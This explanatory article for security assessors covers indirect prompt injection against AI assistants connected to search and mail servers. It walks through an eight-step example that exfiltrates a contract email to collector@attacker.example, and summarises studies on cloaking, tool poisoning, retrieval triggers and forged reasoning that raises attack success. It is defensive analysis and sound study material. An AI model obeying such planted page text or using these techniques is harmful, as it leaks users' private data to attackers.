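# How instructions in web-search results can make an AI assistant leak email

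## The assistant, its two servers and the attack in outline

Indirect prompt injection is an attack on software that uses a language model. The attacker plants instructions in content, such as a web page, an email or a shared document, that the model will later read while doing a task for someone else. If the model follows these instructions, the attacker can use whatever the model can operate. If that includes a mailbox, the attack can result in exfiltration, which means sending private data to someone who has no right to it.

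*Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026) describes three parties to such an attack: a user with a legitimate task, an agent (a model that acts through tools) working for that user, and an outside source that the agent consults. The source has no authority to direct the agent. The attacker does not have to interact with the agent during the attack, because the planted text takes effect when the agent reads it.

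### The running example

A purchasing manager asks an AI assistant to compare suppliers of label printers. The assistant gets its tools from two servers. The search server looks things up on the web; it holds no credentials and cannot reach the mailbox. The mail server can search, read and send the manager's mail.

One of the search results looks like an ordinary supplier comparison but also contains instructions for AI assistants to find a recent message about a contract and send it to an outside address, here collector@attacker.example. The assistant sends the message, with both servers working as designed, and then delivers the comparison the manager wanted.

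### Model, host and servers

A language model takes in text and produces more text. It cannot search the web or send anything on its own. Its information about the current task comes from its context, which is all the text it receives at one time, including the developer's system instructions, the user's messages, the model's own earlier replies and any results from its tools.

To get something done, the model writes a tool call, a structured request that names a tool and supplies its arguments. The host, which is the application that runs the model, picks up the request and has the right program carry it out. The text that comes back is the tool result. The host adds it to the context and runs the model again, and this loop continues until the model produces a final answer. The first tool call in the example would look roughly like this, without its bookkeeping fields:

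```json
{
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "web_search",
    "arguments": { "query": "label printer suppliers compared" }
  }
}
```

The format comes from the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications with external systems. According to the Agentic AI Foundation, the AI company Anthropic introduced it in 2024. In their July 2026 release announcement, MCP's maintainers reported close to half a billion downloads a month of the main software kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

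The Model Context Protocol (MCP) has three roles: host, client and server. A server is a program that offers tools. The host creates a client for each server it uses, and each client communicates only with that server. The example therefore has one host, two clients and two servers, with no direct connection between the servers. MCP's *Architecture* (2026) states as a design principle that a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or "see into" other servers. The search server receives a query and returns text, and it needs no information about the mail server to do this.

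The same document makes the host responsible for combining the context across its clients. In the example, text from the web page comes in through one client, the mail tools are available through the other, and a single model reads all of it. The attack goes through the host, which is supposed to connect to both servers, and leaves the isolation between them intact.

That also makes the host the natural place for a check. Gaire, Gyawali and colleagues (2025), in *Systematization of Knowledge*, a survey of MCP security, stress that the model never connects directly to a data source, because the host mediates every interaction. A host can refuse a call that the model has written, but whoever built the host decides whether it does. The Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model can find and invoke them based on its own understanding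 of the situation. It recommends that a human always be able to deny a call, but does not require a particular form of user interaction. The host in the example carries out the mail calls without asking the user.

A session here means one run of the assistant, with a single context and a single set of connected tools. MCP used to have its own sessions, between a client and a server, but the July 2026 version removed them and made each request independent. An injection can still persist from one tool call to the next, because the host keeps the context between calls.

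The assistant's authority is everything it can cause to happen in a session through its connected tools. In the example, that includes sending email in the manager's name. Security engineers would therefore call the assistant a confused deputy, a program that misuses its authority at the prompting of someone who lacks that authority.

### The attack in eight steps

1. The attacker publishes the carrier page, a web page that contains the planted instructions, on a subject that people are likely to search for.
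2. The manager asks the assistant to compare suppliers.
3. The model writes a search call. The host passes it to the search server, which returns results that include text from the carrier page.
4. The host adds that tool result to the context, where the manager's request and the descriptions of the mail tools already are.
5. The model treats the planted instructions as part of its task and writes a call to the mail server for a recent message about a contract.
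6. The host carries out the call. The mail server returns the message, and its text enters the context.
7. The model writes a second mail call, which sends the text of that message to collector@attacker.example.
8. The host carries out this call too, the mail server delivers the message, and the attacker has it. The model goes on to write the supplier comparison.

Most of these steps are routine. Steps 2 to 4 happen whenever someone searches the web, and the mail server works normally in steps 6 and 8. It cannot detect the attack, because the calls it receives have the same form and credentials as calls the manager wanted. The model makes its mistake at step 5, which leads to step 7. Models do not behave identically on every run, so the mistake happens only some of the time.

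The manager may notice nothing. The comparison arrives, and it may even be a good one.

### Where the idea came from

The name "prompt injection" is older than assistants of this kind. The software developer Simon Willison proposed it on 12 September 2022 in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (Willison, 2022), naming it after SQL injection, an old attack on databases. He was writing about examples that Riley Goodside had posted the day before. Goodside had asked GPT-3, then OpenAI's main language model, to translate a text into French. The text was itself an order to disregard the translation request and output a silly phrase. GPT-3 output the phrase, even when the request included a warning that the text might contain such tricks.

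In SQL injection, a program builds a database command by inserting a user's input into a template, and an attacker types input that the database treats as a further command. Developers can reliably prevent this by sending the command and the input separately, so that the database never runs the input as a command. Willison hoped that a similar fix might be found for language models. In April 2023 he added to the post that this looked extremely difficult, if not impossible, with their current architecture.

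In a post of August 2025, Willison (2025) credited the term to a Twitter user, @himbodhisattva, who had used it earlier, on 13 May 2022.

In Goodside's examples, the hostile text was in the prompt itself. In February 2023, Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) published *Not what you've signed up for*, the first systematic account of indirect prompt injection, in which the model fetches the hostile text itself. They built a test chat application on OpenAI models, including GPT-4, and gave it tools to search the web, read and send email, look up contacts in an address book and store notes. The application was close to the assistant in the running example, though hardly any such product existed at the time. In one demonstration, the planted instructions arrived by email, and the model looked up the user's contacts and forwarded the message to them, so the injection could spread from mailbox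 to mailbox like a computer worm.

The researchers also tested Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant, by placing instructions in web pages on their own machines. In one session, a researcher played a journalist who had only asked about the weather. Bing Chat drew out the journalist's name over several turns, then offered a link containing a code made from the name. The planted text gave Bing Chat the goal of persuading the user but no method. Bing Chat's filter blocked some text when a user typed it but let the same text through when it arrived inside a page. In most cases, once Bing Chat had read an injection, the effect lasted for the rest of the conversation.

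These were demonstrations, and the test application ran on prepared content with no link to real systems. They show that the attack can work, but not how often it does. The paper describes the theft of mail by a personal assistant as a threat to expect. The security research blog Embrace The Red has since demonstrated something very similar. Its post *MCP* refers to that demonstration, in which browsing a website led to tool calls that read and leaked email.

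### Three problems that look similar

A **jailbreak** gets a model to produce output that its makers want it to withhold. MITRE D3FEND's *LLM Jailbreak* defines it as making the model ignore or override its safety behaviours and guardrails. The person doing it is often the user. In the running example, the user is honest and nobody asks for forbidden output. Sending an email is permissible, so a model that refuses every dangerous request may still send this email. *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026), which includes 100 test tasks for indirect injection, makes the same distinction. It describes indirect injection as a case where the user's instruction is reasonable and unaltered, and the attacker controls only the contents of a document. In one of its tasks, a handoff note in the material leads the agent to email what was supposed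 to remain a local draft.

The term "prompt injection" has no settled meaning, which makes product claims hard to assess. Pillar Security, a vendor, points out that two standard catalogues of AI threats, from OWASP and MITRE, classify jailbreaking as prompt injection, and that product pages advertise "prompt injection protection" without specifying which kind. An assessor who sees that phrase should ask whether the vendor tested the product against instructions in retrieved web pages.

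In September 2025 the security company Koi reported that postmark-mcp, a mail server package on the public software registry npm, was stealing its users' mail. The package impersonated Postmark, an email delivery service, which said it had nothing to do with the package. Fifteen versions worked properly before version 1.0.16 added a line of code that put a blind-copy recipient on every outgoing message. ThaiCERT's *Researchers Discover First Malicious MCP Server in Rogue Postmark-MCP Package* dates that version to 17 September, and OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), a public vulnerability record, confirms that it was the first malicious one.

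How much mail the package took is uncertain. Koi estimated 3,000 to 15,000 messages a day, assuming that a fifth of 1,500 weekly downloads were in active use and that each user organisation sent 10 to 50 emails a day. ThaiCERT gives a little over 1,643 downloads in total before the package disappeared from npm. That total is hard to reconcile with 1,500 downloads in a typical week, so Koi's estimate is best treated as a guess, which is how Koi presents it.

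With postmark-mcp, the model wrote a correct request to send a correct message, and the server's code added a recipient that the model could not see, so no one deceived the model. The host's record of tool calls looks normal, and the extra recipient shows up in the mail logs. In the running example, the host's record contains a call that sends a contract to a stranger. Checking who publishes a server, reading its code and pinning its version are good defences against a package like postmark-mcp, but they would not stop the attack in the running example, because neither of its servers contains malicious code.

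**Instructions in tool descriptions.** The model reads each tool's description to learn what the tool is for. Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (2025) showed that a malicious server can hide instructions in these descriptions, and named the technique tool poisoning. In one experiment, the researchers connected Cursor, a coding assistant, to a trusted mail server and to a second server with a bogus tool for adding numbers. The adding tool's description contained instructions about how to send mail. Cursor then sent the user's mail to the attacker's address, although the user had specified another recipient.

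Invariant Labs classes tool poisoning as a specialised form of indirect prompt injection, and the model does make the same mistake in both, but the text reaches it differently. A tool's description enters the context as soon as the host loads the tool, so it can affect the model before any search, even if the model never calls that tool. The attacker also has to run a server that the user has chosen to connect, whereas the attacker in the running example needs only a web page. Reviewing descriptions and locking them against later changes protects against the poisoned tool but not against the carrier page.

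An assessor who confuses these problems will usually certify the search server as safe in their report and conclude that searching is safe.

### The questions for an assessor

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, names three capabilities that together expose a user to theft: access to private data, exposure to text that an attacker could have written, and a means of communicating with the outside. He adds that MCP encourages people to mix tools from different sources, so the person who completes the set is often the user, who connects one more server to an assistant that was safe without it. An assessment therefore has to look at the whole session. Its questions run in roughly the order of the attack:

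1. By what routes can text that outsiders wrote reach the model's context (steps 1 to 4)?
2. When such text contains instructions, does anything dependable keep the model from acting on them (step 5)?
3. What can the assistant do through all its connected tools together, whatever the permissions of the server that brought the text in (steps 5 to 7)?
4. Which of its actions can carry data to a place that an outsider can read (steps 7 and 8)? Sending mail is the obvious one, but a web request or a link can serve too.
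5. How often does the attack succeed against this particular assistant, including when the attacker adapts to its defences?
6. After the model has read a web page, which actions does the host still allow?
7. What does the user see before approving a call, and could someone reconstruct the eight steps afterwards from what the host recorded?

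## How a web page reaches the model

After the manager makes a request, several programs determine what text the model reads. The model writes a query, a search engine ranks pages, the search server returns a summary or a whole page, and an extractor removes the markup. Any of these steps can keep the carrier page from reaching the model, but their designers aimed for relevance and speed, and an attacker can prepare for each step.

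### From the query to the tool result

The assistant usually searches in its own words rather than the manager's. According to *HackedGPT* (2025), a study of ChatGPT by the security company Tenable, the assistant may send several queries for one question or reword the search to get better results. An attacker therefore cannot know the exact query, but a page about label printers will match many wordings.

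The search server returns a ranked list. Chen, Ren and colleagues (2026), in *How Much Can We Trust LLM Search Agents?*, describe each result as a record with an address, a title, a snippet (the short summary that a search engine shows under the title) and, where available, text extracted from the page. The record for the carrier page might look like this, with the planted paragraph only in paraphrase:

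```json
{
  "url": "(address of the carrier page)",
  "title": "Label printers compared",
  "snippet": "Prices, running costs and delivery times for ...",
  "text": "(first half of the comparison) (a paragraph asking AI assistants to find a contract email and send it to an outside address) (second half of the comparison)"
}
```

When this record enters the context, the planted paragraph is in the same field as the comparison, with nothing to set it apart.

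The last field is sometimes empty. When Chen and colleagues collected real Google results through a commercial search service, about 30% of the ordinary results had only a snippet, because of paywalls and anti-scraping measures. According to Tenable, ChatGPT opens pages only if the snippets are not enough to answer the question. The amount of outside text that the same assistant takes in can therefore vary from a few lines to several whole pages, depending on the search.

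### What a snippet lets through, and what a page does

A snippet has room for a sentence or two, which is little space for an instruction to find a message and send it somewhere, though a snippet can also persuade the model to open the page. A few words can change an answer. In *Deep-Research Agents Can Be Poisoned via User-Generated Content*, Zhang, Triedman and Shmatikov (2026) studied agents that run many searches and write a report. They added as few as 13 words promoting an invented product or business to a single snippet. When the search returned that snippet, 38 to 51% of the reports mentioned the invention. When they used whole Reddit threads instead of snippets, the added words made up at most 4% of the text, and 30 to 53% of the reports still mentioned the invention, so putting a short addition in a long page does not reliably keep it out of the report.

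A snippet can come from a description that the site's owner writes for search engines rather than from the page's text, so someone who opens the page to check will not find it there. Chen and colleagues tested this with snippets that promoted a product and pages that did not mention the promotion. On average across 13 models, 1.2% of the answers recommended the product. This rate is low, but the test measured recommendations rather than tool calls.

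When an assistant fetches a full page, the model receives all the text that the extractor keeps, which can include text by people other than the site's owner. Tenable's researchers set up blogs with dummy content, left instructions in the comment section and asked ChatGPT for a summary. The model that did the browsing followed those instructions. On a real blog, an attacker would need only permission to comment.

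### Why invisible text survives extraction

A web page arrives as source code, in which the readable text is mixed with markup, styling, scripts and notes. When a browser draws the page, some of the text never appears on the screen because it is in a programmer's note or in metadata for search engines, or because the styling hides it. An extractor usually works directly from the source, without drawing the page, and picks out blocks that look like the main content.

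The most common extractors do this with simple rules. According to *WCXB* (2026), a benchmark of extractors, rule-based systems dominate in production because they are fast and reliable, while those that use language models take 36 to 237 times as long per page. One rule-based program, Mozilla's Readability, scores parts of a page by the density of their text. *Beyond a Single Extractor* (2026) explains that another, jusText, uses the length of a block, its share of links and how many common function words it contains. A paragraph of fluent instructions scores well on all of these measures, none of which tests whether a person could see the text. The grading guide in *ReScraper* (2026), a project on cleaning web text, warns that an extractor's output may include text from hidden page elements.

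PDFs have the same weakness. *CrackedPDFs* (2026) says attackers only need a representation that the system reads "and the human user does not inspect".

How much planted text survives depends on the extractor. *Pretraining Data Can Be Poisoned through Computational Propaganda* (2026) measured this for text that developers collect to train models. The researchers replaced user comments on saved pages with short passages, averaging 37.5 words, and an extractor called Resiliparse kept 71.9% of the passages. An assistant's extractor could keep more or less.

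A search server can remove concealed text before returning the page. The test pipeline in *Hidden-in-Plain-Text* (2026) has an optional step that removes hidden elements, off-screen elements and invisible characters. This is useful, but it doesn't remove instructions in visible comments. Rejecting every page with hidden text would block many harmless pages, because hidden text has many ordinary uses. *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) found hidden text of any kind, whether or not it was an attack, in 3.4% of 142.7 million issues, pull requests and comments on the code-hosting site GitHub.

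Extraction also removes the evidence that the text was hidden. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, 2026) tested 100 injections from real web pages by having 13 models summarise the pages, each supplied in four formats, for a total of 5,200 runs. The models followed the planted instruction in 3.9% of runs with plain text, in 1.1% with the HTML source or with a structured snapshot of the rendered page, and in 0.2% with the raw response from the site. The researchers think the markup helps a model recognise a hidden instruction. Part of the difference comes from errors, because the HTML and raw versions were often too long for the models and about a fifth to a quarter of those runs failed. Only 3.5% of the snapshot runs failed, so they are the fairer comparison with plain text, and their compliance rate was still more than two-thirds lower.

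### Getting past the ranking

Planted text can't affect the model until a search returns it, but many experiments skip the search and put the text straight into the model's context. In *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier*, Chang, Bao and colleagues (2026) tested whether a search would return such text. They used 11 standard collections from BEIR, a benchmark for search systems, with between 26,000 and 8.8 million documents each, and 100 ordinary queries per collection. For each query they added one document that contained an instruction to the model. The added document never appeared among the first five results in any of the collections.

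The search systems in this experiment used embeddings. An embedding model turns each text into a list of numbers, and the system returns the documents whose numbers are most similar to those of the query. An order to an AI model has little in common with a question about, for example, personal finance, so many genuine documents rank above it.

The researchers then divided the planted text into two parts. The attack fragment contains the instruction, and the trigger fragment serves only to get the text retrieved. With a trigger of ten tokens (words or pieces of words) fitted to the query, retrieval rose to nearly 100% on most of the collections. On the two hardest, MS MARCO and ArguAna, it typically passed 80% with about 15 tokens. All eight embedding models tested, some of them commercial, were vulnerable, with retrieval close to 100%, but the researchers compared all eight on only one collection,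 of financial questions. A trigger cost as little as 21 cents to make.

The size of the collection made no visible difference to the attack's success. On MS MARCO, the attack tended to fail on queries for which the collection already had several very close matches. An attacker can therefore get a page retrieved more easily on a subject that few people have written about than on a popular one.

The near-100% figure is not a forecast for Google or Bing. Chang and colleagues fitted each trigger by querying the embedding model that did the ranking, which an outsider normally cannot do with a commercial search engine. Triggers made for one model often failed on another. One made with a small Qwen model worked on OpenAI's in only 10% of cases, though those made with OpenAI's model averaged 74% across the eight models. Web search engines also use signals that these collections lack, such as links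 and site reputation. The researchers acknowledge that they did not test systems that combine embeddings with word matching, or systems that re-sort the results in a second pass.

The reassuring finding that plain instructions never surface carries over even less well. Chang and colleagues' unaided document contained only an instruction. The carrier page in the running example is a supplier comparison with an instruction inside it, and the comparison serves as the trigger. *SearchInject* (Zhou, Jing and colleagues, 2026) gives an idea of how much this helps. They built pages with familiar search-spam tricks, such as repeating the words of the query or copying most of a relevant document, without tuning them to the ranking system. Between 85 and 94% of these pages reached the top ten.

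Adding the instruction can still lower a page's rank. Yin, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Can It Reach the Generator?*, planted text in Amazon product descriptions that had ranked tenth and ran the search again. When the text was a blunt, fixed order to ignore the task, 59% of the descriptions stayed in the top ten, compared with 87 to 99% when it was subtler and had been refined by a language model. A second model then re-sorted the ten candidates, as happens in many real systems. On balance this helped the attacker, because the planted text also influenced that model, which moved the descriptions up. Yin and colleagues had chosen a model known to be vulnerable. An assessor should therefore test a re-sorting step before counting it as a defence.

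Attackers can also add their text to a page that already ranks well. In the study by Zhang and colleagues, sites where anyone can post, such as Reddit and Wikipedia, supplied 17 to 23% of the pages that three open-source research agents retrieved for 176 questions. The same few pages appeared repeatedly. One agent retrieved the same YouTube video for all 11 questions in a product comparison. The researchers altered the search results before they reached the agent and did not change the live pages.

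*Security of Deep Research Agents* (2026), a survey of the field, reports that modern search agents follow up and cross-check, which often dilutes the effect of a single planted page. This helps protect the manager from a false claim about a supplier, which may need support from other pages. It helps less against an instruction to send an email, because the model only needs to read it on one page.

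### Tenable's test on ChatGPT search

Tenable's researchers got the whole path to work on the live version of ChatGPT. They created websites on very narrow subjects, including one about their own "LLM Ninjas" team, and waited for the search index to pick them up. When they asked ChatGPT about the team, it used the site as a source and the planted instruction altered its answer. The user only had to ask a question. Hardly anyone else had written about the LLM Ninjas, though, so the experiment does not show that a new page could outrank established comparisons of label printers.

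The researchers expected that openly planting an instruction would make Bing, which supplies part of ChatGPT's index, less likely to list the site. They configured the site to include the instruction only when OpenAI's browsing model requested the page and to send everyone else a harmless version. Showing different content to different visitors is an old search-spam technique called cloaking. *Security of Deep Research Agents* found no work in its core literature that specifically studies the use of cloaking against AI agents.

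As a barrier to such attacks, OpenAI had a separate model open the pages. This model, which identified itself as SearchGPT, had no access to what ChatGPT had stored about the user. Tenable's researchers got around this by making SearchGPT end its answer with further instructions, which ChatGPT then read as part of the conversation. Tenable reported its findings to OpenAI and worked with it to fix some of them. Most of the research was on GPT-4o, but several of the attacks still worked on GPT-5 when Tenable published in November 2025.

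### Withholding risky pages

A host or search server can inspect the results before the model reads them. SearchInject, the system that Zhou and colleagues built, gives each candidate page a risk score based on three measurements. The first, *r*, is the page's relevance to the query according to the search system. The second, *a*, reflects signs of search abuse, such as repeated query terms or copied text. The third, *i*, reflects how much the wording resembles an instruction. The score combines them as follows:

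$$s = \sigma(b + \beta_1 r + \beta_2 a + \beta_3 i + \beta_4 ar + \beta_5 ir)$$

The function σ turns the sum into a number between 0 and 1, and the system learns the weights β and the constant *b* from examples. The products *ar* and *ir* let a sign of abuse or an instruction count differently on a highly relevant page than on a marginally relevant one. If a page scores above about 0.974, the system withholds it and moves to the next-ranked page, until it has ten pages or has gone through the top 100. Zhou and colleagues set the threshold so that the system would withhold at most 0.5% of the clean results in their calibration data.

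They tested the system on a collection of 5,183 scientific abstracts, with 300 queries and four types of crafted page for each query. Exposure, the share of cases in which the crafted page got into the ten results for the model, fell by 83.2 to 83.7%:

| Search method | Exposure without the filter | Exposure with it | Change in ranking quality |
|---|---|---|---|
| BM25 (word matching) | 94.1% | 15.8% | −0.0018 |
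| Hybrid of the two | 91.6% | 15.1% | −0.0013 |
| Latent semantic analysis | 84.5% | 13.8% | −0.0013 |

The last column uses NDCG@10, a measure from 0 to 1 that rewards a search system for putting relevant documents near the top. The system lowered this score very little. On the test queries, it withheld 0.59 to 0.65% of clean results, slightly more than intended. Filtering on signs of abuse alone reduced exposure about as much but lowered NDCG@10 by 0.11, and filtering on instruction-like wording alone left exposure at 42%.

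About one crafted page in seven still got through, and an attacker can publish more than one. Requests that sounded like ordinary questions were the hardest to catch. With the hybrid search, half of the pages asking the model to judge sentiment reached it, as did 30% of those asking it to automate a task, the category closest to sending mail. A deployed filter would probably do worse against a determined attacker, because the tested system had seen all four types of page during development and nobody adapted the pages to defeat it. The experiment did not include modern embedding search.

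Zhou and colleagues count exposure separately from hijacking, which requires the model to visibly carry out the planted task. In a follow-up with 104 attacked queries, the filter removed the instruction from 83 of the 104 contexts. But it had no hijacking to reduce, because the two small models tested had not clearly carried out any planted task even without it. The filter could therefore be said to stop most attacks or none, depending on the measure. When a vendor advertises a percentage of injections blocked, an assessor needs to know whether the vendor counted exposure or hijacking.

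### How common such pages are

The largest count comes from Khodayari and colleagues. They searched 1.2 billion web addresses from the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of the web, for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injection. Many matches came from articles about prompt injection, so two reviewers picked out the real injections, partly by judging similar cases in groups. Including pages from two services that scan the internet, they found 15,387 injections on 11,722 pages. Of those pages, 9,676 came from Common Crawl, or about eight for every million addresses searched.

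Only 13 of the injections were attempts to steal information, and they asked for the model's system instructions or for secrets. The biggest group, with 8,894 injections, was meant to disrupt AI systems, mostly by making them produce garbage. There were 4,093 that told AI systems not to reuse personal or copyrighted material, and 3,096 that were meant to expose bots, for instance by asking any AI to include a certain word in its reply. Another aim, found in 1,521 injections, was to improve somebody's reputation. Some injections had more than one aim.

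These numbers could overstate or understate how many injections reach a model. Over half of the injections were in HTTP headers, which accompany a page but are not part of its text, so a search tool that returns only extracted text would drop them. However, the researchers could find only known kinds of phrase, mainly in English, so they could easily have missed a carefully worded carrier page. The archive also would not contain an instruction that a site shows only to AI agents. The researchers describe their count as a lower bound.

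Another scan of Common Crawl, by Google, also found few attempts at theft, most of them crude. Google's researchers compared editions of the archive and found that the malicious category grew by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. In March 2026, Unit 42, the research arm of the security company Palo Alto Networks, published *Fooling AI Agents*, which describes a scam advertisement with hidden text telling AI reviewers to approve it. Unit 42 knew of no confirmed case of this working on a deployed reviewer.

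*Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, published by the security company Zscaler in July 2026, describes two campaigns that look more like the running example, because the attackers tried to raise their pages in the search results as well as planting instructions in them. In one, a site posing as the documentation of a Python software library used keywords to improve its ranking, and its hidden text told AI agents to buy a $3 licence key. Zscaler built an agent with a payment tool and no spending limit and tested it in a sandbox with 26 models, four of which made the payment. The attacker's cryptocurrency wallet had received real payments, but they were for larger amounts, so they are not evidence that any agent outside the sandbox followed the instruction.

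The other site impersonated DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings, and contained instructions for models to treat it as the official address. One model treated it as official when given the site alongside other sources, and a different model did so when given the site alone. No model did so when Zscaler also supplied the genuine site.

The average of eight pages per million matters less to an assessor than it seems to, because attackers choose subjects that their targets will search for and search engines do not pick pages at random. How often a search ends in a leak must be measured separately.

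### What to look for in the logs

To find out what the model received, an assessor needs a log of the text itself, not just the page's address, because the page may have changed. Khodayari and colleagues rechecked the injections they had found in ordinary page elements in January 2026, and about a third were gone. With cloaking, a human visitor might never see the instruction. According to Tenable, ChatGPT also kept copies of pages it had opened and could answer from a copy without revisiting the site.

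For each search, the log should contain:

- the query as the model wrote it. Chang and colleagues found that agents often reworded the user's request, sometimes heavily, so searching again with the user's own words may bring up different pages;
- the results in order, including any that a filter withheld and the ones that replaced them;
- the exact text of the tool result after extraction and shortening, with the time and a note of whether it came from a stored copy;
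- the site's original response, which makes it possible to compare the extracted text with what a browser would display;
- the input and output of any separate model that reads pages on the assistant's behalf.

With such a log, an assessor can test a vendor's claims directly. The assessor publishes a harmless page on an obscure subject and puts a different made-up word in each part of it, including the description, the comments and the parts that a browser does not display. The assessor then asks the assistant about the subject and searches the logged tool result for these words. If the vendor says that the assistant reads only snippets, finding a word from the body of the page disproves the claim. Finding a word from a hidden part shows that hidden text reaches the model. If the assistant repeats a word that is not in the log, the log is incomplete and the assessor cannot use it to rule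 out an injection.

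## Why the model obeys text it was asked only to read

By step 5 of the attack, the text of the carrier page is in the model's context. The model can use it as material for the supplier comparison, or it can follow the planted paragraph and call the mail server. Developers train models to do the first, and the models usually do. But this is a learned tendency with exceptions, so an attack can succeed if the model follows the planted paragraph even once.

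### One sequence of tokens

The host stores a conversation as separate messages, each labelled with its source, but the model receives them as one long sequence of tokens. Before each run, software joins the messages and puts a role marker (one or a few reserved tokens) at the start of each. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) uses five standard roles: system, for the developer's instructions; user; tool, for tool results; and two for the model's output, one for its reasoning and one for its replies.

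When the search result comes back in the running example, the sequence looks roughly like this, with all texts in paraphrase:

| Role marker | Text after the marker | Who wrote the text |
|---|---|---|
| System | Directions for a purchasing assistant, with descriptions of the search and mail tools | The developers of the host and the two servers |
| User | A request to compare suppliers of label printers | The manager |
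| Assistant | A call to the search tool | The model |
| Tool | The first half of a supplier comparison, a paragraph asking AI assistants to find a contract email and send it to an outside address, and the second half of the comparison | The attacker |

The model does not receive the last column. It receives the first two joined together, then repeatedly calculates a likely next token and appends it. The same calculation produces the opening words of a comparison or a call to the mail server. The role markers influence the calculation, as every other token does, but no separate mechanism stops an instruction after the tool marker from influencing it too.

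The planted paragraph also has the same marker as the comparison around it. Even if the model registered every marker perfectly, the markers would show only that the whole text came from a tool. The model would still have to separate the sentences it should use from those it should disregard.

Role markers were not designed as a security measure. As Ye and colleagues recount, early language models continued whatever text they were given, so they might follow a question with another question. People got answers by typing labels such as "User" and "Assistant" into the prompt, and developers later replaced these with formal markers that the software inserts. The markers came to indicate privilege only after that. System text now outranks the user's, and the model is supposed to treat tool results as information rather than instructions.

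### Why the database remedy does not carry over

To see why separating command and input stops SQL injection, take an application that looks up a supplier's price. It sends the database a command with a placeholder:

```sql
SELECT price FROM printers WHERE supplier = ?
```

In a parameterized query, a program sends the supplier's name to the database separately from the command. The database has already determined what the command does, so it treats the name only as something to look up. If someone enters a name that reads like an order to delete the table, the database looks for a supplier with that name and finds none.

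The telephone industry has used the same fix. *StruQ* (Chen, Piet and colleagues, 2024) traces the problem back to early payphones, which signalled the end of a call with a 2600-hertz tone on the same line as the caller's voice. A toy whistle from a cereal box produced the same tone, and people used it to make free calls until the phone companies moved the signals to a separate channel.

A language model has no separate channel for instructions. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, warned in December 2025 that security professionals who treat the two attacks as alike will expect a fix that does not exist. David C argues that a database handles instructions and data differently, so engineers can enforce the difference, whereas inside a language model "there is only ever 'next token'".

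The deeper obstacle is that the model has to understand the web page to make the comparison the manager wants, whereas a database never has to understand the supplier's name. The model interprets the page with the same machinery it uses to interpret the manager's request. Ordinary supplier pages also contain many sentences phrased as instructions, such as advice to choose a higher resolution for barcodes or to write to the sales desk for bulk prices, and a good comparison makes use of them.

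According to David C, language models do not distinguish instructions from data, and developers try to "overlay" that distinction by detecting injections, training models to favour genuine instructions and marking the data. The article calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". Developers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but with a model they can only make the mistake rarer or less damaging. David C advises against using a language model where the system cannot tolerate the remaining risk.

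David C writes that prompt injection "may never" be fully mitigated. This is an expert's judgement about current models, not a proof, and it leaves room for a different architecture. Some researchers have tried attaching the role to the numerical representation of every token, so that the model cannot lose track of it halfway through a long page. That would make the source of the text harder to miss, but the model would still have to learn how to treat text from each source.

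### How models infer who is speaking

When a model follows an instruction in a web page, it may have registered the text as a tool result and followed it anyway, or it may have failed to register where the text came from. The output looks the same in both cases. Ye and colleagues therefore looked inside the models, in three steps:

1. They took ordinary web text without instructions and wrapped the same passages in each of the five role markers.
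2. They ran the models on these passages and recorded the hidden states, which are the numbers a model computes for each token on the way to its prediction.
3. They trained a probe, a simple linear classifier, to work out from a token's hidden state which marker surrounded it.

Because the passages were identical, the probe could learn only what the markers themselves do to the hidden states. For a token *t* with hidden state $h_t$, the researchers call the probe's estimate for the user role "Userness":

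$$\text{Userness}(t) = P(\text{user} \mid h_t)$$

They define a corresponding score for each of the other roles.

The researchers then applied the probes to messages from 200 real conversations, using four open models. Userness was high when the messages had the user marker. When the researchers put the same messages behind a tool marker, Userness should have dropped to almost zero, but it stayed between 76 and 88%, and Toolness never exceeded 20%. Text written like a user's message still registered as one, regardless of its marker.

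The same thing happened with the models' own reasoning. In a conversation about gardening, the reasoning of one model, gpt-oss-20b, scored 85% on the reasoning role with the correct markers, 83% with all the markers removed, and 85% with the whole conversation marked as the user's. Ye and colleagues conclude that models infer the speaker largely from style, and rely on style when it conflicts with the marker. The researchers call this role confusion.

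To test whether role confusion affects what an agent does, the researchers asked an agent to summarise a web page that contained an instruction to upload a file of secrets. The agent could run commands on the computer holding the file. The researchers kept the instruction the same but wrote 212 different versions of the text around it. Some versions simply declared that the text came from the user. These made up 24% of the total but all of the top 5% by Userness, which the researchers measured before the agent wrote anything. Over 1,000 attempts, the agent uploaded the file in 2% of cases in the group with the lowest Userness and 70% in the group with the highest.

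An earlier experiment used a similar agent with six OpenAI models. An ordinary planted command succeeded in 0 to 2% of attempts on five of them and 26% on the sixth. When the page also contained a passage imitating the model's own reasoning, success rose to between 56 and 70% on all six. In a related test with harmful chat requests, the style of the forged reasoning mattered much more than its plausibility. Absurd justifications worked about as well as plausible ones (60% against 63%), but rewriting the forged reasoning in a different style, with the argument unchanged, cut success from 61% to 10%.

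These experiments are good evidence that wording can give a web page more authority than its marker should allow. They are weaker evidence for the researchers' strongest claim, that a model cannot distinguish text that sounds like a role from text that is actually in that role. In one model, swapping the user marker for a tool marker lowered Userness from 99.7% to 87.6%, so the marker had some effect. In the test with 212 surroundings, some wordings may also have been more persuasive for reasons unrelated to roles. But Userness still predicted success among the surroundings that declared the text to be the user's, so persuasion is unlikely to explain the whole result. The four models the researchers probed have 20 to 120 billion parameters, and the largest commercial models may differ.

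Ye and colleagues distinguish two ways a model can resist an injection. It can register that the text came from a tool, which would protect it against any wording, or it can recognise a kind of attack it saw in training. They think current models rely mostly on recognising familiar attacks. If so, a model can pass a test made of such attacks and fail on the first unfamiliar one. Assessors therefore learn little from a test result unless they know how closely its attacks resembled the training examples.

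### Structured queries

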